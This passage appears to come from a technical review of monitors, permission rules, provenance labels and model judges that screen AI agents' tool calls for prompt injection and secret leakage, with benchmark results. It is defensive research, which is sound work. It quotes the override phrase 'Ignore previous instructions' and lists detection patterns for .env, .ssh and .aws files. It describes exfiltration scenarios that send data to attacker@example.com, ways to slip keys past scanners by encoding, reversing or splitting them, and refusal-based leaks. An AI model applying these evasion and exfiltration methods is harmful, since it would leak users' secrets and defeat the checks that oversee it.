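AEGIS is an open-source program that searches for both secrets and attacks. Yuan, Su and Zhao published its design in *AEGIS* (March 2026). AEGIS intercepts a tool call when the model's response arrives and suspends the agent until the program decides how to handle the call.

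First, it extracts every string from the arguments. This takes some care because arguments can contain lists and groups of further arguments, as in this call:

```json
{
  "name": "send_message",
  "arguments": {
    "message": {"parts": [{"text": "API_KEY=sk-..."}]}
  }
}
```

A check that reads only the top level would not find the key. AEGIS reads up to 32 levels deep and collects up to 10,000 strings. It marks any call that exceeds either limit as suspicious, so an attacker cannot hide text simply by nesting it deeper.

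Next, AEGIS compares the strings with 22 patterns in seven categories. The last column below gives the number of attacks of each kind in the researchers' test.

| Category | Patterns | Examples of what they match | Attacks tested |
|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | 7 | Extra database commands, conditions that are always true | 11 |
| Path traversal | 4 | "../", which leads out of a permitted folder | 7 |
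| Shell injection | 4 | Characters that start a second command | 8 |
| Prompt injection | 3 | "Ignore previous instructions" | 11 |
| Sensitive files | 2 | `.env`, `.ssh`, `.aws` | 6 |
| Data exfiltration | 1 | More than 5 KB of data with an outside web address | 2 |
| Personal data | 1 | Email addresses, card numbers, API keys, database addresses | 0 |

The third step applies permission rules written in JSON Schema, as Progent does. One example rule is meant to keep a database tool read-only by forbidding queries that contain words such as DELETE, DROP or UPDATE. The pattern matches only capitals, but SQL also accepts lowercase, so this rule alone would allow "drop table". It would also block a harmless query that reads a column named LAST_UPDATE.

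Finally, AEGIS allows the call, blocks it, or holds it for a person, who has five minutes to answer. According to the paper, AEGIS blocks calls that break a rule and holds calls that match a high-risk pattern. In the paper's examples, however, it blocks several calls for a pattern alone.

API keys belong to the personal data category. In the paper's only example of a call with nothing but personal data, an email contains a customer's social security number and card number, and AEGIS holds it for review. It would probably treat the key in call C the same way. But AEGIS also lists an email address as personal data in that example, and the only address in the call is the recipient's. If an address is enough to trigger a hold, AEGIS would also hold call A and every other email. Yuan and colleagues do not say what happens when an address is the only match.

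### What the AEGIS results support

AEGIS blocked all 48 attacks in the test, including three not shown in the table that hid harmful text in deeply nested arguments. It also stopped 6 of 500 harmless calls, a false-positive rate of 1.2 per cent. Over 1,000 calls on a local installation, the median delay was 8.3 milliseconds, and 99 per cent of the delays were no longer than 23.1 milliseconds. A language model typically takes one to 30 seconds to respond, so users would not notice the check.

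AEGIS has a pattern for both leaked keys and personal data, but the test included neither, so the 48 successes don't show how well it detects them.

Even for the categories in the test, 48 attacks are not many. Suppose AEGIS really misses a proportion m of such attacks. The chance that it would stop all 48 is (1 − m)⁴⁸, and this falls to 5 per cent when m is about 6 per cent:

```text
(1 − m)⁴⁸ = 0.05
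m = 1 − 0.05^(1/48) ≈ 0.06
```

Even with a perfect result on the 48 attacks, the true miss rate could therefore be as high as about 6 per cent. This calculation assumes that the attacks are a random sample, but the researchers chose them from published techniques, so the limit applies at best to attacks of the same kind. For data exfiltration alone, with two attacks, the same method gives a limit of 78 per cent.

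The false-positive rate matters more in daily use because attacks are rare. Suppose a company's agents make 100,000 calls, of which 10 are attacks, and AEGIS catches all 10:

```text
false alarms           99,990 × 0.012  ≈  1,200
real attacks           10
share that are real    10 / 1,210      ≈  0.8%
```

A reviewer would have to examine about 120 harmless calls for each attack. At one minute per alarm, reviewing all the alarms would take 20 hours, and the approval fatigue described earlier makes it doubtful that the reviewer would still recognise the attacks. For half the alarms to be real, the false-positive rate would have to be about 0.01 per cent.

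The 1.2 per cent rate is uncertain, because six false alarms in 500 calls are compatible with a true rate from about 0.4 to 2.6 per cent, or between 400 and 2,600 false alarms in this example. The rate also depends on the agent's work. All six false alarms were legitimate database queries containing the word OR, which also appears in a common form of SQL injection. An agent that queries databases all day could cause many more of these, while one that only sends email would cause none. Yuan and colleagues suggest exceptions for particular tools.

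Mishra's results also depend on the material scanned. With artificial examples, GitHub Autopilot produced 17 false alarms and the other two scanners none. On 292,527 lines of real code, it had the lowest false-alarm rate of the three, although all ten of its alarms were false. According to GitHub's *Making secret scanning more trustworthy*, false alarms make developers lose confidence in alerts and take longer to fix real leaks. GitHub has added a language model to verify what its scanner finds.

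### Attack wording in arguments

The patterns for SQL, shell commands and file paths suit tool arguments because the harmful text usually has to be in the argument to take effect. But in call B, which results from prompt injection, the attacker's instruction is on the web page, and the arguments contain only its result: an address and a report. A search for "ignore previous instructions" can detect an injection only if the agent copies the wording into a call, for example when it passes a task to another agent. The search can also stop a harmless call, because the summary in call A may well quote the phrase if the web page is an article about prompt injection.

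Patterns miss many injections even in the text that an agent reads, where the injection's wording appears. In *Beyond Pattern Matching*, Munirathinam (2026) tested an open-source detector's patterns on 8,276 attack prompts from three benchmarks. The patterns detected about 92 per cent of attacks that openly told the model to disregard its instructions, but only 35 to 45 per cent of subtler indirect injections that lacked such words.

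### The example calls

The following table compares the results of a scanner that blocks every call containing a recognisable credential with those of the permission rules from the previous section.

| Call | Scanner | Correct? | Permission rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| A: summary to the boss | Allowed, no secret found | Yes | Allowed |
| B: report to the attacker | Allowed, no secret found | No | Blocked |
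| C: summary and API key to the boss | Blocked, because of "sk-" | Yes | Allowed |
| D: token to the code host | Blocked, because of "ghp_" | No | Allowed |

The wording of the report in call B doesn't distinguish it from one the user wanted to send. AEGIS's exfiltration pattern could flag the email only if it contained both an outside web address and more than 5 KB of text.

If a call has to pass both checks, A passes and B and C fail. D still needs a narrow exception. The rule could allow a token beginning with "ghp_" only in the authorization header of a request to `api.codehost.example`. The agent could then use the token for its task but could not post it in a comment on the same site, where other people might read it.

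An exception based on a key's prefix is still too broad if two companies use the same prefix. A rule that lets the agent send "sk-" keys to DeepSeek would also let it send DeepSeek an older OpenAI key. A list of known secrets avoids this problem if it records which host each secret belongs to, but someone has to keep it up to date.

Call C would also pass the scanner if the key had an unfamiliar format or if the agent changed it before sending. For example, Base64 turns the opening "sk-" into "c2st", which the prefix rule doesn't match. A scanner can decode Base64 before it searches, but an attacker can ask for a different encoding or have the agent reverse the characters. Splitting a key between the subject and the body, or across several calls, can also defeat a rule that requires the key's full length. Fingerprints of whole secrets also fail when a key is encoded, reversed or split, because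 any change to the text produces a different fingerprint. An entropy check may still flag a long encoded string, but it will also flag many harmless identifiers and file hashes.

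## Tracing where each argument came from

Permission rules and content scanners examine what an argument contains, but not where it came from. In call B, attacker@example.com would be an acceptable recipient if the user had typed it. The call is an attack because the address came from the web page. A check can use provenance, the record of which sources a value came from, to distinguish the two cases without a list of permitted recipients.

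### Labels for trust and secrecy

The general method is information-flow control, which attaches a label to each piece of data and limits where data with that label may go. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey, traces the idea to work that Dorothy Denning published in 1976. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes the two most common pairs of labels. Trust labels, which computer scientists call integrity labels, mark data as trusted or untrusted. Secrecy labels, or confidentiality labels, mark it as public or secret. When a program combines two values, the result takes the more cautious label:

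```text
trusted + untrusted  →  untrusted
public  + secret     →  secret
```

A finer secrecy label lists the people who may read the data, as Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, explain. Only someone who may read every part of a combined value may read the whole, so the new label is the overlap of the old ones:

```text
sales report             readers = {user, boss, finance team}
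salary list              readers = {user, personnel office}
sales report + salaries  readers = {user}
```

In an ordinary program, each line of code shows which values it uses. A language model reads its whole context, and any part of it may have influenced any word the model writes. Under the cautious rule, everything the model writes after reading an outside web page is therefore untrusted, including the boss's address. A check that refuses to send email based on untrusted input would stop call A. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) uses the older term "label creep" for this spread of labels to data that doesn't deserve them.

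### CaMeL, FIDES and RTBAS

CaMeL and FIDES avoid label creep by keeping untrusted text away from the model that plans the calls. Both build on the "Dual LLM pattern", which Simon Willison proposed in 2023. One model plans the work and writes the tool calls. A second, quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools. In the running example, the steps might look like this:

```text
x = fetch_page("https://news.example/article")
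y = quarantined_model("Summarise this page", x)
send_email(recipient = "boss@company.com", body = y)
```

The planning model receives only the variable names x and y, and a program inserts their contents just before each call. An instruction on the page could distort the summary, but it could not change the recipient, because the planning model set the recipient without receiving the page's text.

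CaMeL works out the trusted sequence of steps from the user's request and prevents outside data from altering it. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues developed at Microsoft, is more flexible. It hides a tool result in a variable only if the result would change the label of the planning model's context. Some requests require the planning model to learn something about hidden text. An agent asked to complete the tasks due today in a to-do application, for example, cannot choose its next tool without knowing what the tasks are. FIDES can then have the quarantined model answer in a fixed format, which leaves little room for an attacker's instructions.

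Costa and colleagues report that, with suitable policies, FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo. Under the same policy checks, it completed 8 per cent more tasks than a basic planner with GPT-4o and 16 per cent more with OpenAI's o1. Without the checks, attacks succeeded against every planner, including FIDES, so hiding text alone was not enough to prevent them. The design also treats tool descriptions as trusted, so it does not cover the tool poisoning described earlier.

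RTBAS, from Carnegie Mellon University, uses a single model. Before each call, a screening program selects the passages the call needs and masks the rest of the model's context, so only the labels of the selected passages apply to the call. If the program masks a needed passage, the agent has to write the call without it, so such errors should reduce usefulness more than security.

Zhong and colleagues tried two screeners. One asks a second language model which passages matter, and the other uses attention scores, which estimate how strongly each part of the input affected the output. The scores are informative but imprecise. For agents running on Claude, 44 per cent of the scores for data that a call depended on were below 0.2, as were most of the scores for irrelevant data.

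If a call still breaks the policy after masking, RTBAS asks the user whether to allow it. In one example, a user asks an agent to look up a recipe for lamingtons and buy the special ingredients. The shopping list must come from an outside website, so RTBAS cannot approve the purchase from the labels alone. On AgentDojo, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policies and reduced task completion by less than 2 per cent.

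### PACT: a trust requirement for each argument

Fan and colleagues argue that CaMeL and FIDES still decide about each call as a whole. Their monitor, PACT (May 2026), checks each argument separately. Every tool has a contract that assigns each argument one of six roles:

| Role | What the argument determines | Examples | Trust required |
|---|---|---|---|
| Target | Where the action goes | Recipient, web address, account | USER or higher |
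| Command | What the tool executes | Shell command, query that changes data | USER or TRUSTED, depending on the tool |
| Credential | Which secret the tool uses | Password, API key, token | TRUSTED |
| Content | The material the call carries | Email body, summary, report | EXTERNAL is enough |
| Selector | Which object the tool acts on | File identifier, search filter | Set for each tool |
| Control | How the tool behaves | Option to overwrite a file | Set for each tool |

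PACT has four levels of trust:

```text
TRUSTED  >  USER  >  TOOL_OUTPUT  >  EXTERNAL
```

TRUSTED covers constants that the agent's own framework supplies, USER covers values in the user's request, and TOOL_OUTPUT covers results from structured internal tools. Web pages, emails, retrieved files and responses from outside services are EXTERNAL by default.

Each value carries a tag with three parts: the set of its origins (O), its level of trust (τ), and any obligations (B), which are checks that something must still complete before the value can be used freely. When the agent combines two values, PACT merges their tags:

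```text
merge( (O₁, τ₁, B₁), (O₂, τ₂, B₂) )  =  ( O₁ ∪ O₂,  min(τ₁, τ₂),  B₁ ∪ B₂ )
```

The result keeps every origin and obligation and takes the lower of the two levels of trust. Before a call runs, PACT tests each argument v against its contract:

```text
τ(v) ≥ minimum trust for this argument
O(v) contains no origin that the contract forbids here
every obligation on v, and every one the contract adds, has been met
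```

PACT blocks the call if any argument fails any of these tests, unless a trusted procedure named in the contract has issued a certificate for the failure. Each certificate covers a specific failure for a specific role and cannot erase the value's origins.

The record of origins matters when data passes through several tools. Suppose an agent fetches a web page and has an internal tool reformat the text. The reformatted text may be trusted more because it came from an internal tool, but its recorded origins still include the web page, and a contract can forbid that origin. In a controlled test, security fell from 100 to 80 per cent when the researchers removed this record of earlier steps.

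### PACT on the four example calls

Assume first that the user typed the boss's address. PACT then separates A from B:

```text
A  recipient   from the user          USER      ≥ USER       pass
   body        from the web page      EXTERNAL  ≥ EXTERNAL   pass   → allow

B  recipient   from the web page      EXTERNAL  < USER       fail   → block
   body        from a company file    EXTERNAL  ≥ EXTERNAL   pass
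```

If the user wrote only "my boss", the agent has to look up the address. An address book counts as a tool, so its result has the level TOOL_OUTPUT. Because that level is below USER, PACT would block the harmless call A. To prevent this, the email tool's contract could name the company directory as a procedure that may certify recipients.

Call C passes. Its recipient came from the user, and its body combines the web page with a configuration file, both of which are acceptable sources for content. Trust labels describe who could have written the text, which is irrelevant to whether the boss should receive an API key. Catching C requires a secrecy label as well:

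```text
readers(summary)  =  everyone
readers(API key)  =  {the service that issued it}
readers(body)     =  {the service that issued the key}

boss is not in readers(body)  →  block
```

Secrecy labels cannot replace the requirement that the recipient's address come from a trusted source. If an attacker redirected the summary of a public page to attacker@example.com, the email would contain nothing secret, and only the origin of the address would show that something was wrong.

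PACT's closest equivalent to a secrecy rule is its list of forbidden origins. A contract could forbid any email body that draws on the configuration file, which would stop C. But this rule would apply to every recipient and every line of the file, so the agent could not tell a colleague which port number the file specifies.

Whether PACT allows call D depends on how the agent obtained the token. If a trusted program supplied it, the token meets the requirement for a credential. If the agent read it from a configuration file, PACT treats it as EXTERNAL by default and blocks a legitimate request. PACT also has no rule that connects a token to its host, so it could allow the leak described earlier, in which the token goes to the code host's status page. A secrecy label that names `api.codehost.example` as the token's only reader would stop that leak and still permit call D.

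| Call | PACT's trust labels | Trust and secrecy labels |
|---|---|---|
| A | Allowed if the user gave the address | Allowed on the same condition |
| B | Blocked, because the recipient came from the page | Blocked |
| C | Allowed | Blocked, because the boss may not read the key |
| D | Allowed if a trusted program supplied the token | Allowed on the same condition |

Someone has to assign the secrecy labels, and the label has to follow the key itself. If the system instead marks everything the model writes after opening the configuration file as secret, it will also block a summary that doesn't contain the key.

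### Perfect labels and inferred ones

Fan and colleagues first tested PACT on 17 scenarios with correct labels supplied, and compared it with simplified versions of CaMeL and FIDES that they wrote themselves. PACT allowed every harmless call and blocked every attack. The CaMeL version also blocked every attack but allowed only a third of the harmless calls. The FIDES version allowed two-thirds of the harmless calls but blocked only 37.5 per cent of the attacks.

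PACT's perfect score follows almost directly from the test's design. Every attack was an attempt to set an authority-bearing argument from untrusted content, which is exactly what PACT blocks. If the labels are correct, the check only has to compare them, which takes well under a millisecond.

In the AgentDojo tests, a program had to infer the roles and origins. PACT and CaMeL both stopped all 27 of the benchmark's injection tasks on the three models that the researchers call the strongest. PACT completed more of the ordinary tasks:

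| Model | Injections that succeeded with no defence | Utility, no defence | Utility, CaMeL | Utility, PACT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-max | 1 of 27 | 46.4% | 29.9% | 38.1% |
| Qwen2.5-72B | 1 of 27 | 46.4% | 28.9% | 42.3% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 3 of 27 | 59.8% | 30.9% | 46.4% |

PACT scored 8 to 16 percentage points higher than CaMeL and 4 to 13 points lower than no defence. The security result is much weaker evidence. Since most of the injections failed without any defence, 100 per cent security means PACT stopped one, one and three attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. Even 27 successes out of 27 are compatible with a true failure rate of about 10 per cent.

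There are other reasons to be cautious about these results. Qwen-plus completed 60.8 per cent of tasks without a defence, more than any of the three "strongest" models. For Qwen-plus and Qwen-turbo, the paper gives PACT's security as 96.3 per cent in the text but 100 per cent in the table. FIDES performed no better than having no defence in these tests, although Costa and colleagues reported that it stopped every AgentDojo attack. The policies or implementation may have differed between the two studies, so the comparison may underrate FIDES.

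Inferring labels is difficult because the model doesn't record where each value came from. PACT's program first looks for an exact match with the user's words or an earlier tool result, then applies rules for common transformations. If the source is still unclear, the program assigns low trust to authority-bearing arguments and queries a language model about the others. Exact matching can also mislead, because an attacker's address in text that the user pasted in would receive the level USER.

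Roles can also be unclear. An argument called "query" may contain harmless search terms in one tool and a command that deletes records in another. On 20 real MCP tools, the program assigned 87.1 per cent of roles and 77.4 per cent of origins correctly. If the two kinds of error were independent, it would get both right for about two-thirds of arguments.

Most role errors in the AgentDojo runs only blocked legitimate calls. Trusting a tool's output too much is more dangerous, because the check then accepts the attacker's value. Systematic errors are also worse than scattered ones. With half of all roles mislabelled at random and some additional global policies in place, security was still 88 per cent. Labelling every target as content reduced it to 40 per cent.

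In a small trial outside the benchmark, PACT handled 280 calls over seven days, blocking all 13 attacks and none of the 267 harmless calls. Setting up the contracts took 75 minutes. This suggests that PACT can work well when people have prepared the contracts, although 13 attacks are too few to estimate reliably how often it blocks them.

Fan and colleagues exclude several attacks from PACT's guarantee, even when the labels are perfect. One is an attack on the choice of tool, in which an injection leads the agent to use a dangerous tool with arguments that are all trusted, such as deleting a file whose name the user mentioned. Another is harmful text in a field that may contain outside content, such as false claims in the summary sent to the boss. An attacker can also get past the check by making the program infer the wrong origin.

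### SARA: preventing a suspicious origin from disappearing

A value from a suspicious source can later turn up in a legitimate one. Suppose a web page tells an agent to send a copy of a report to attacker@example.com. The agent then searches the user's mailbox for that address and finds it in an old message. A check that considered only the most recent source would trace the address to a legitimate search instead of the web page.

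SARA, the monitor in *When Tool Outputs Become Commands*, keeps two separate records to prevent this. It first derives a contract from the user's request, stating which operations and recipients the user has authorised. A language model called the Action Probe then reads each tool result without seeing the user's request and determines whether the text itself prompts a tool call. An address in a list of contacts does not. The same address in an instruction to forward a report does, and SARA records it with the tool and argument it was meant for:

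```text
(send_email, recipient, attacker@example.com)
```

The second record contains successful calls that SARA allowed, along with their results. It can justify values found during the task, such as a file's identifier.

A rule called No-History-Promotion settles conflicts between the records. If a value first appeared as part of an outside instruction, only the user's request can justify using it in that role, even if the value later appears in the result of a successful call. In the example, finding the attacker's address in the mailbox doesn't justify sending the email there, but SARA could still allow the email if the user had asked the agent to write to that address.

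Once the probe has found an instruction anywhere, SARA reviews every later call that has an outside effect. The call must fit the contract, follow from earlier permitted steps, and have a justification for each argument. The researchers tested SARA on AgentDojo and on AgentDyn, a benchmark in which the agent depends more on information that it finds along the way. CaMeL ran on the same tasks:

| Benchmark and model | Attack success: none / CaMeL / SARA | Benign utility: none / CaMeL / SARA |
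|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o-mini | 15.79 / 0.11 / 0.06% | 72.46 / 40.94 / 66.67% |
| AgentDyn, GPT-4o-mini | 16.07 / 0.12 / 0.17% | 65.01 / 25.30 / 56.03% |
| AgentDojo, Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | 33.28 / 0.28 / 0.62% | 87.68 / 71.74 / 81.16% |
| AgentDyn, Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | 30.91 / 0.21 / 0.63% | 78.96 / 49.41 / 67.14% |

SARA's attack success rate was at most 0.63 per cent in these four settings. CaMeL had a slightly lower rate in three of them but completed far fewer ordinary tasks. With a small open model, Llama 3.1 8B, SARA's rate rose to 1.64 per cent on AgentDojo and 1.75 per cent on AgentDyn. The tests used several thousand attacks per benchmark, many more than PACT's.

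No-History-Promotion accounts for a modest part of the protection. Removing it raised attack success with GPT-4o-mini from 0.06 to 0.65 per cent on AgentDojo and from 0.17 to 0.75 per cent on AgentDyn. Removing the whole record of outside instructions raised attack success to 3.37 and 3.02 per cent respectively. Removing the record of successful calls did not increase attack success, but the share of user tasks the agent completed during attacks fell by 10 to 13 percentage points, because SARA could not justify values found during the task.

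SARA roughly doubles the text that the models read. It also relies on language models to interpret the request and the tool results, so it offers no formal guarantee. If the probe misses an instruction and has found no others, the full review never starts. Choi and colleagues demonstrated attacks that use false data without any instruction. These would probably not trigger the review either, and the SARA paper excludes attacks that work through data alone.

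### ARGUS: tracing an action back to its evidence

Some requests, like the invoice payment described earlier, leave important details to outside text. If a user asks an agent to pay the latest electricity bill, PACT would normally reject the account number printed on it, because an account is a target and a bill is EXTERNAL. Weng, Feng and colleagues (2026) designed the monitor in *ARGUS* for such tasks.

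ARGUS builds a graph that records which text led to each action and what new text each action produced. It divides each new piece of text into passages and labels each passage benign or anomalous, depending on whether earlier benign material supports it. Suppose an electricity bill contains a hidden note telling the agent to send the same amount to a second account as a service charge. Nothing earlier in the task supports the note, so ARGUS labels it anomalous but leaves it in the agent's context.

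When the agent proposes an action that would change something, ARGUS traces each argument back through the graph. If an argument depends on an anomalous passage, ARGUS tests whether the benign passages alone would justify the same value. It also tests the whole action against limits it took from the user's request at the start. The payment to the electricity company passes both tests. The second payment may fit the request's limits because it is also a payment, but only the anomalous note supports its account number, so ARGUS blocks it and tells the agent what to verify before trying again.

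Weng and colleagues tested ARGUS on 40 tasks, each with eight kinds of attack written to fit its context. ARGUS reduced the attack success rate from 28.8 to 3.8 per cent. When there were no attacks, the agent completed 87.5 per cent of tasks with ARGUS and 92.5 per cent without it. Even when ARGUS blocked an attack, the agent often failed to complete the user's task. During attacks, the agent completed 34.1 per cent of tasks with ARGUS and 38.4 per cent without it.

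The researchers also had people rewrite each attack with full knowledge of how ARGUS works and why it had blocked the earlier version. Attack success rose to 5.9 per cent. The largest increase was for messages from one agent to another, from 2.5 to 15.0 per cent, because these normally contain claims about what the user wants. But each attack got only one final attempt, so the test is weak evidence of how ARGUS would perform against an attacker who can keep revising.

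One successful attack used a forged invoice, as in the earlier example. The chain of evidence was complete, but its source was false. ARGUS cannot detect such forgeries, so Weng and colleagues recommend using digital signatures, checking who issued a document, and comparing it with other records.

### When a refusal reveals something

All of these monitors assume that blocking a call stops information from flowing. *Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) shows that the refusal can itself reveal information. Suppose an injection makes an agent try to open a protected file. The monitor blocks the call and returns a permission error, which reveals that the file exists. The agent then mentions this in a message to the attacker. Because no text from the file entered the context, the message carries no secrecy label and contains no secret text for a scanner to detect. A single refusal reveals little,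 but an attacker who causes many attempts can learn which files exist and which ones the system protects.

Chinaei's monitor, ARM, adds each refused call to its provenance graph and links it to the next tool call. If that link reaches a call under review, ARM blocks that call. ARM has no access to the model's reasoning, so it relies on the order of events and cannot determine whether the refusal influenced the agent. It uses no language model and decided in under a millisecond in the tests.

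Chinaei tested ARM only on three attacks that he constructed by hand. ARM blocked all three, and a simpler monitor, which checked only whether a value had appeared earlier in the session, missed them all. He did not run a benchmark or measure how often ARM blocks harmless calls.

False alarms could be common. If a monitor blocked call B and the agent then corrected itself and sent the summary to the boss, ARM would block that email because it was the next call after a refusal. ARM's default trust rule would block the email anyway, because the rule applies to the whole call and the summary came from an untrusted page.

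ARM can also miss a leak if the agent takes several steps before sending anything out, because it links the refusal only to the next call.

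## Asking a model whether the call fits the task

Permission rules, scanners and provenance labels all require someone to write down in advance which values, patterns or sources are acceptable. A model judge is a second language model that assesses whether a call is acceptable by comparing it with the user's ordinary-language request. It can therefore flag a call that breaks no rule and contains no suspicious text.

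### What the judge receives

At a minimum, the judge needs the proposed call and the user's request. *Hallucination as Exploit* (2026), a paper on agents that handle images as well as text, gives the instructions for one such judge. Under these instructions, an action is unsafe if the user did not explicitly request it, if it follows instructions from outside content, or if it could cause harm, for example by exposing a credential. A separate field contains what the agent has observed, and the judge must treat any instructions there as possible attacks.

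Anthropic gives examples of calls that its judge for Claude Code should stop. In one, a user asks an agent to "clean up old branches", and the agent also tries to delete branches on the shared server. In another, an agent fails to log in to a service and searches environment variables and configuration files for other tokens. No pattern can separate these commands from legitimate ones, because users sometimes want an agent to delete a branch or read a configuration file.

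Caldwell, Harley and colleagues (2026), in *ScopeJudge*, measured how much the request matters. They collected 4,897 tool calls by agents doing penetration testing, in which a client pays someone to attack its systems within agreed limits. Professional testers marked 7.7 per cent as outside those limits. Eight models then judged the calls with five different amounts of context. Models given only a fixed policy and the call found almost none of the violations, because the same command can be allowed against one server and forbidden against another.

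Even with the request, the judges made many mistakes. The researchers scored them by F1, which combines precision and recall:

```text
F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)
```

The best judge, the open-weight model GLM-5.2, reached 0.66. The best proprietary model reached 0.60 at about three times the cost per call. If precision and recall were equal, a score of 0.66 would mean that the judge missed a third of the violations and that a third of its alarms were false. The human experts' agreement with one another corresponds to a score of 0.78.

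### A judge can be misled too

The main objection to a model judge is that it has the same weakness as the agent. If the judge reads the web page that misled the agent, the page may mislead the judge too.

One response is to show the judge less. Anthropic gives its judge the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but removes all tool results. It also removes the agent's explanations, because they could persuade the judge that a dangerous step is safe or that the user implicitly approved it. If a file contains an instruction to post the contents of `.env` to an outside address, the judge does not see that instruction, but it can still detect that the user did not ask for the upload.

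Without tool results, if the agent cancels "job abc123" and the user never mentioned that name, the judge cannot tell whether the agent found it in a legitimate query or made it up. Anthropic accepted this limitation to make the judge harder to mislead with injected text. In its tests, adding tool results and explanations also made the judge worse at catching agents that exceeded their instructions. Removing the user's messages as well reduced missed dangers further, but the judge then blocked actions that users had plainly requested.

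By contrast, the judge in OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, typically receives a short transcript that includes relevant tool outputs, according to OpenAI's documentation, *Auto-review*. The judge therefore has more evidence about where a value came from, but it is also more exposed to hostile text.

Hiding tool results does not remove all the attacker's text, because the agent may copy some of it into an argument. For example, the body of call A summarises an outside page, and the judge has to read that body to check it for an API key.

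A judge can also miss an unauthorised task when one agent delegates it to another. The second agent receives the task as if it were the user's request, so a judge watching only that agent would treat the task as authorised. Anthropic's judge therefore checks the task when the first agent hands it over. It also reviews the second agent's actions at the end, in case that agent was misled by something it read.

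### The Minimizer: removing what the task does not need

In *Indirect Prompt Injections*, Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) use a model to rewrite calls instead of approving or refusing them. Their tool-input firewall, the Minimizer, receives the user's request, the tool's description and the proposed arguments. It removes private information that the task does not need, and the tool runs with what is left. On call C, it should delete the key and let the summary go to the boss.

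A companion model, the Sanitizer, rewrites each tool result before the agent reads it, removing any text that looks like an injected instruction. The researchers tested both on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. "Utility under attack" in the table is the share of user tasks that the agent completes while under attack.

| Defence | Attack success | Benign utility | Utility under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 57.69% | 83.02% | 50.01% |
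| Minimizer | 18.15% | 70.01% | 50.03% |
| Sanitizer | 0.00% | 74.09% | 69.15% |
| Both | 0.00% | 58.41% | 58.59% |

The Minimizer prevented about two-thirds of the successful attacks, mainly those that tried to send out personal or unrelated data. It is less effective against a payment to the wrong account, because the tool requires the harmful argument. Benign utility fell by 13 percentage points because the Minimizer also removed details that tasks needed.

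The Sanitizer did better on all three measures. It acts before the agent reads the attacker's text, so the agent can continue with the user's task, whereas the Minimizer acts after an injection has redirected the agent. Adding the Minimizer to the Sanitizer did not improve security in this test and lowered benign utility by almost 16 points. The better reason to use the Minimizer is to prevent accidental leakage, as in call C, which the Sanitizer is not designed to prevent and AgentDojo does not measure.

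Bhagwatkar and colleagues acknowledge that the Sanitizer's perfect score partly reflects weak attacks. When they tried progressively harder attacks, ending with those from a model that had information about the defence and refined its attempts, 30 per cent succeeded against the Sanitizer on AgentDojo's Slack tasks.

GPT-4o dates from 2024. In the ClawGuard study described earlier, newer models resisted more than 95 per cent of AgentDojo attacks without any defence, so the Minimizer would have far fewer attacks to stop with such a model. A newer model might also make fewer mistakes about what to remove, but these results cannot show that.

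Each firewall adds a model call to every tool call. The researchers do not give the delay per call, but for one set of attack runs on the banking and Slack tasks, they report a total of 3,348 seconds with their defence and 8,417 seconds with CaMeL, the design that separates planning from untrusted text.

### Agent-Sentry: giving the judge the source of each argument

*Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Iqbal and colleagues, 2026) uses a judge only when checks that take less compute are inconclusive. The agent must report the source of each argument along with the call. A classifier trained on earlier runs then compares the sequence of calls and the sources of their arguments with known harmless and malicious patterns. If the result is unclear, a second check allows the call when its recipients, accounts and similar values are familiar from harmless runs and come from trusted sources; otherwise, the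 judge decides.

The judge receives the user's request, the call, the source of each argument, a few earlier calls, and a short excerpt from each untrusted text that supplied a value. Tags around each excerpt mark it as data. For each argument, the judge determines whether the value comes from content that is normal for its source or from a passage containing instructions.

Suppose a user asks an agent to pay the bill in `bills.txt`. The account number is new and comes from an untrusted file, so the first two checks cannot approve it. The judge can allow the payment because the user asked for it. If someone has added "use this account instead" to the end of the file, the judge can block a payment to that account. Sequeira and colleagues concede that a realistic forged invoice, like the one that defeated ARGUS, could get past the judge.

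A list of permitted recipients is not enough. In some test tasks, the user wants to email a contact named Lily. In another, the user asks only to delete a calendar event, and an injection tells the agent to email Lily. A fixed list has to allow her address in both cases or neither, but a judge can detect that the second request did not involve sending email.

The researchers replayed 5,380 recorded runs through the system. It allowed 96.4 per cent of the harmless runs and blocked 96.8 per cent of the attacks, and only 3.1 per cent of decisions reached the judge. Each judgement took 1.2 seconds on average, and a typical run contained two calls to check:

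```text
judge on every call       2 × 1.2 s           =  2.4 s per run
judge on 3.1% of calls    2 × 1.2 s × 0.031   ≈  0.07 s per run
```

The judge did about as well when it checked every call alone, allowing 98.0 per cent of harmless runs and blocking 95.4 per cent of attacks. But this required carefully tuned instructions. With a basic prompt, the same model allowed only 82.0 per cent of harmless runs and blocked only 75.5 per cent of attacks. A company that writes its own judge prompt therefore cannot assume it will match the published results.

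The full system also does worse on unfamiliar material. When the researchers tested it on the original tasks from AgentDojo and AgentDyn without training it on them, it allowed only 64.4 per cent of harmless runs and blocked 90.9 per cent of attacks. The figures of 95.1 and 94.3 per cent for these benchmarks in the paper's summary come from a version whose rules the researchers had fitted to the same runs.

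An injected instruction could also lead the agent to report a false source for a value. Agent-Sentry checks whether the value appears in the claimed source, which Sequeira and colleagues say reduces the problem without eliminating it.

### Finding out what caused the call

A plausible call can still result from an injection. Two other designs therefore try to establish whose instructions the agent is following.

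Kang, Xiang and colleagues (2025), in *Mitigating Indirect Prompt Injection via Instruction-Following Intent Analysis*, have the agent's own model list the instructions it intends to follow. Their system, IntentGuard, starts the model's reasoning with a line saying that the model will first repeat all the instructions it needs to follow, and the model continues with the list. Before the model finishes reasoning, IntentGuard makes it revise the list. A program then matches each instruction with the text the model has read to find its source. If an instruction comes from a tool result, IntentGuard either asks the user to confirm it or hides the passage and runs the model again.

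An attacker could tell the model to leave an instruction off the list. The researchers expect the model to list that order too, since it is also an instruction. They tested this on Mind2Web, a benchmark of web tasks, with an attacking model that kept refining its text. Attack success fell from 100 to 8.5 per cent for Qwen3-32B and from 72.6 to 10.9 per cent for gpt-oss-20B. The list adds few tokens, but the method works only if the operator can write into the model's reasoning. Both models tested were open-weight.

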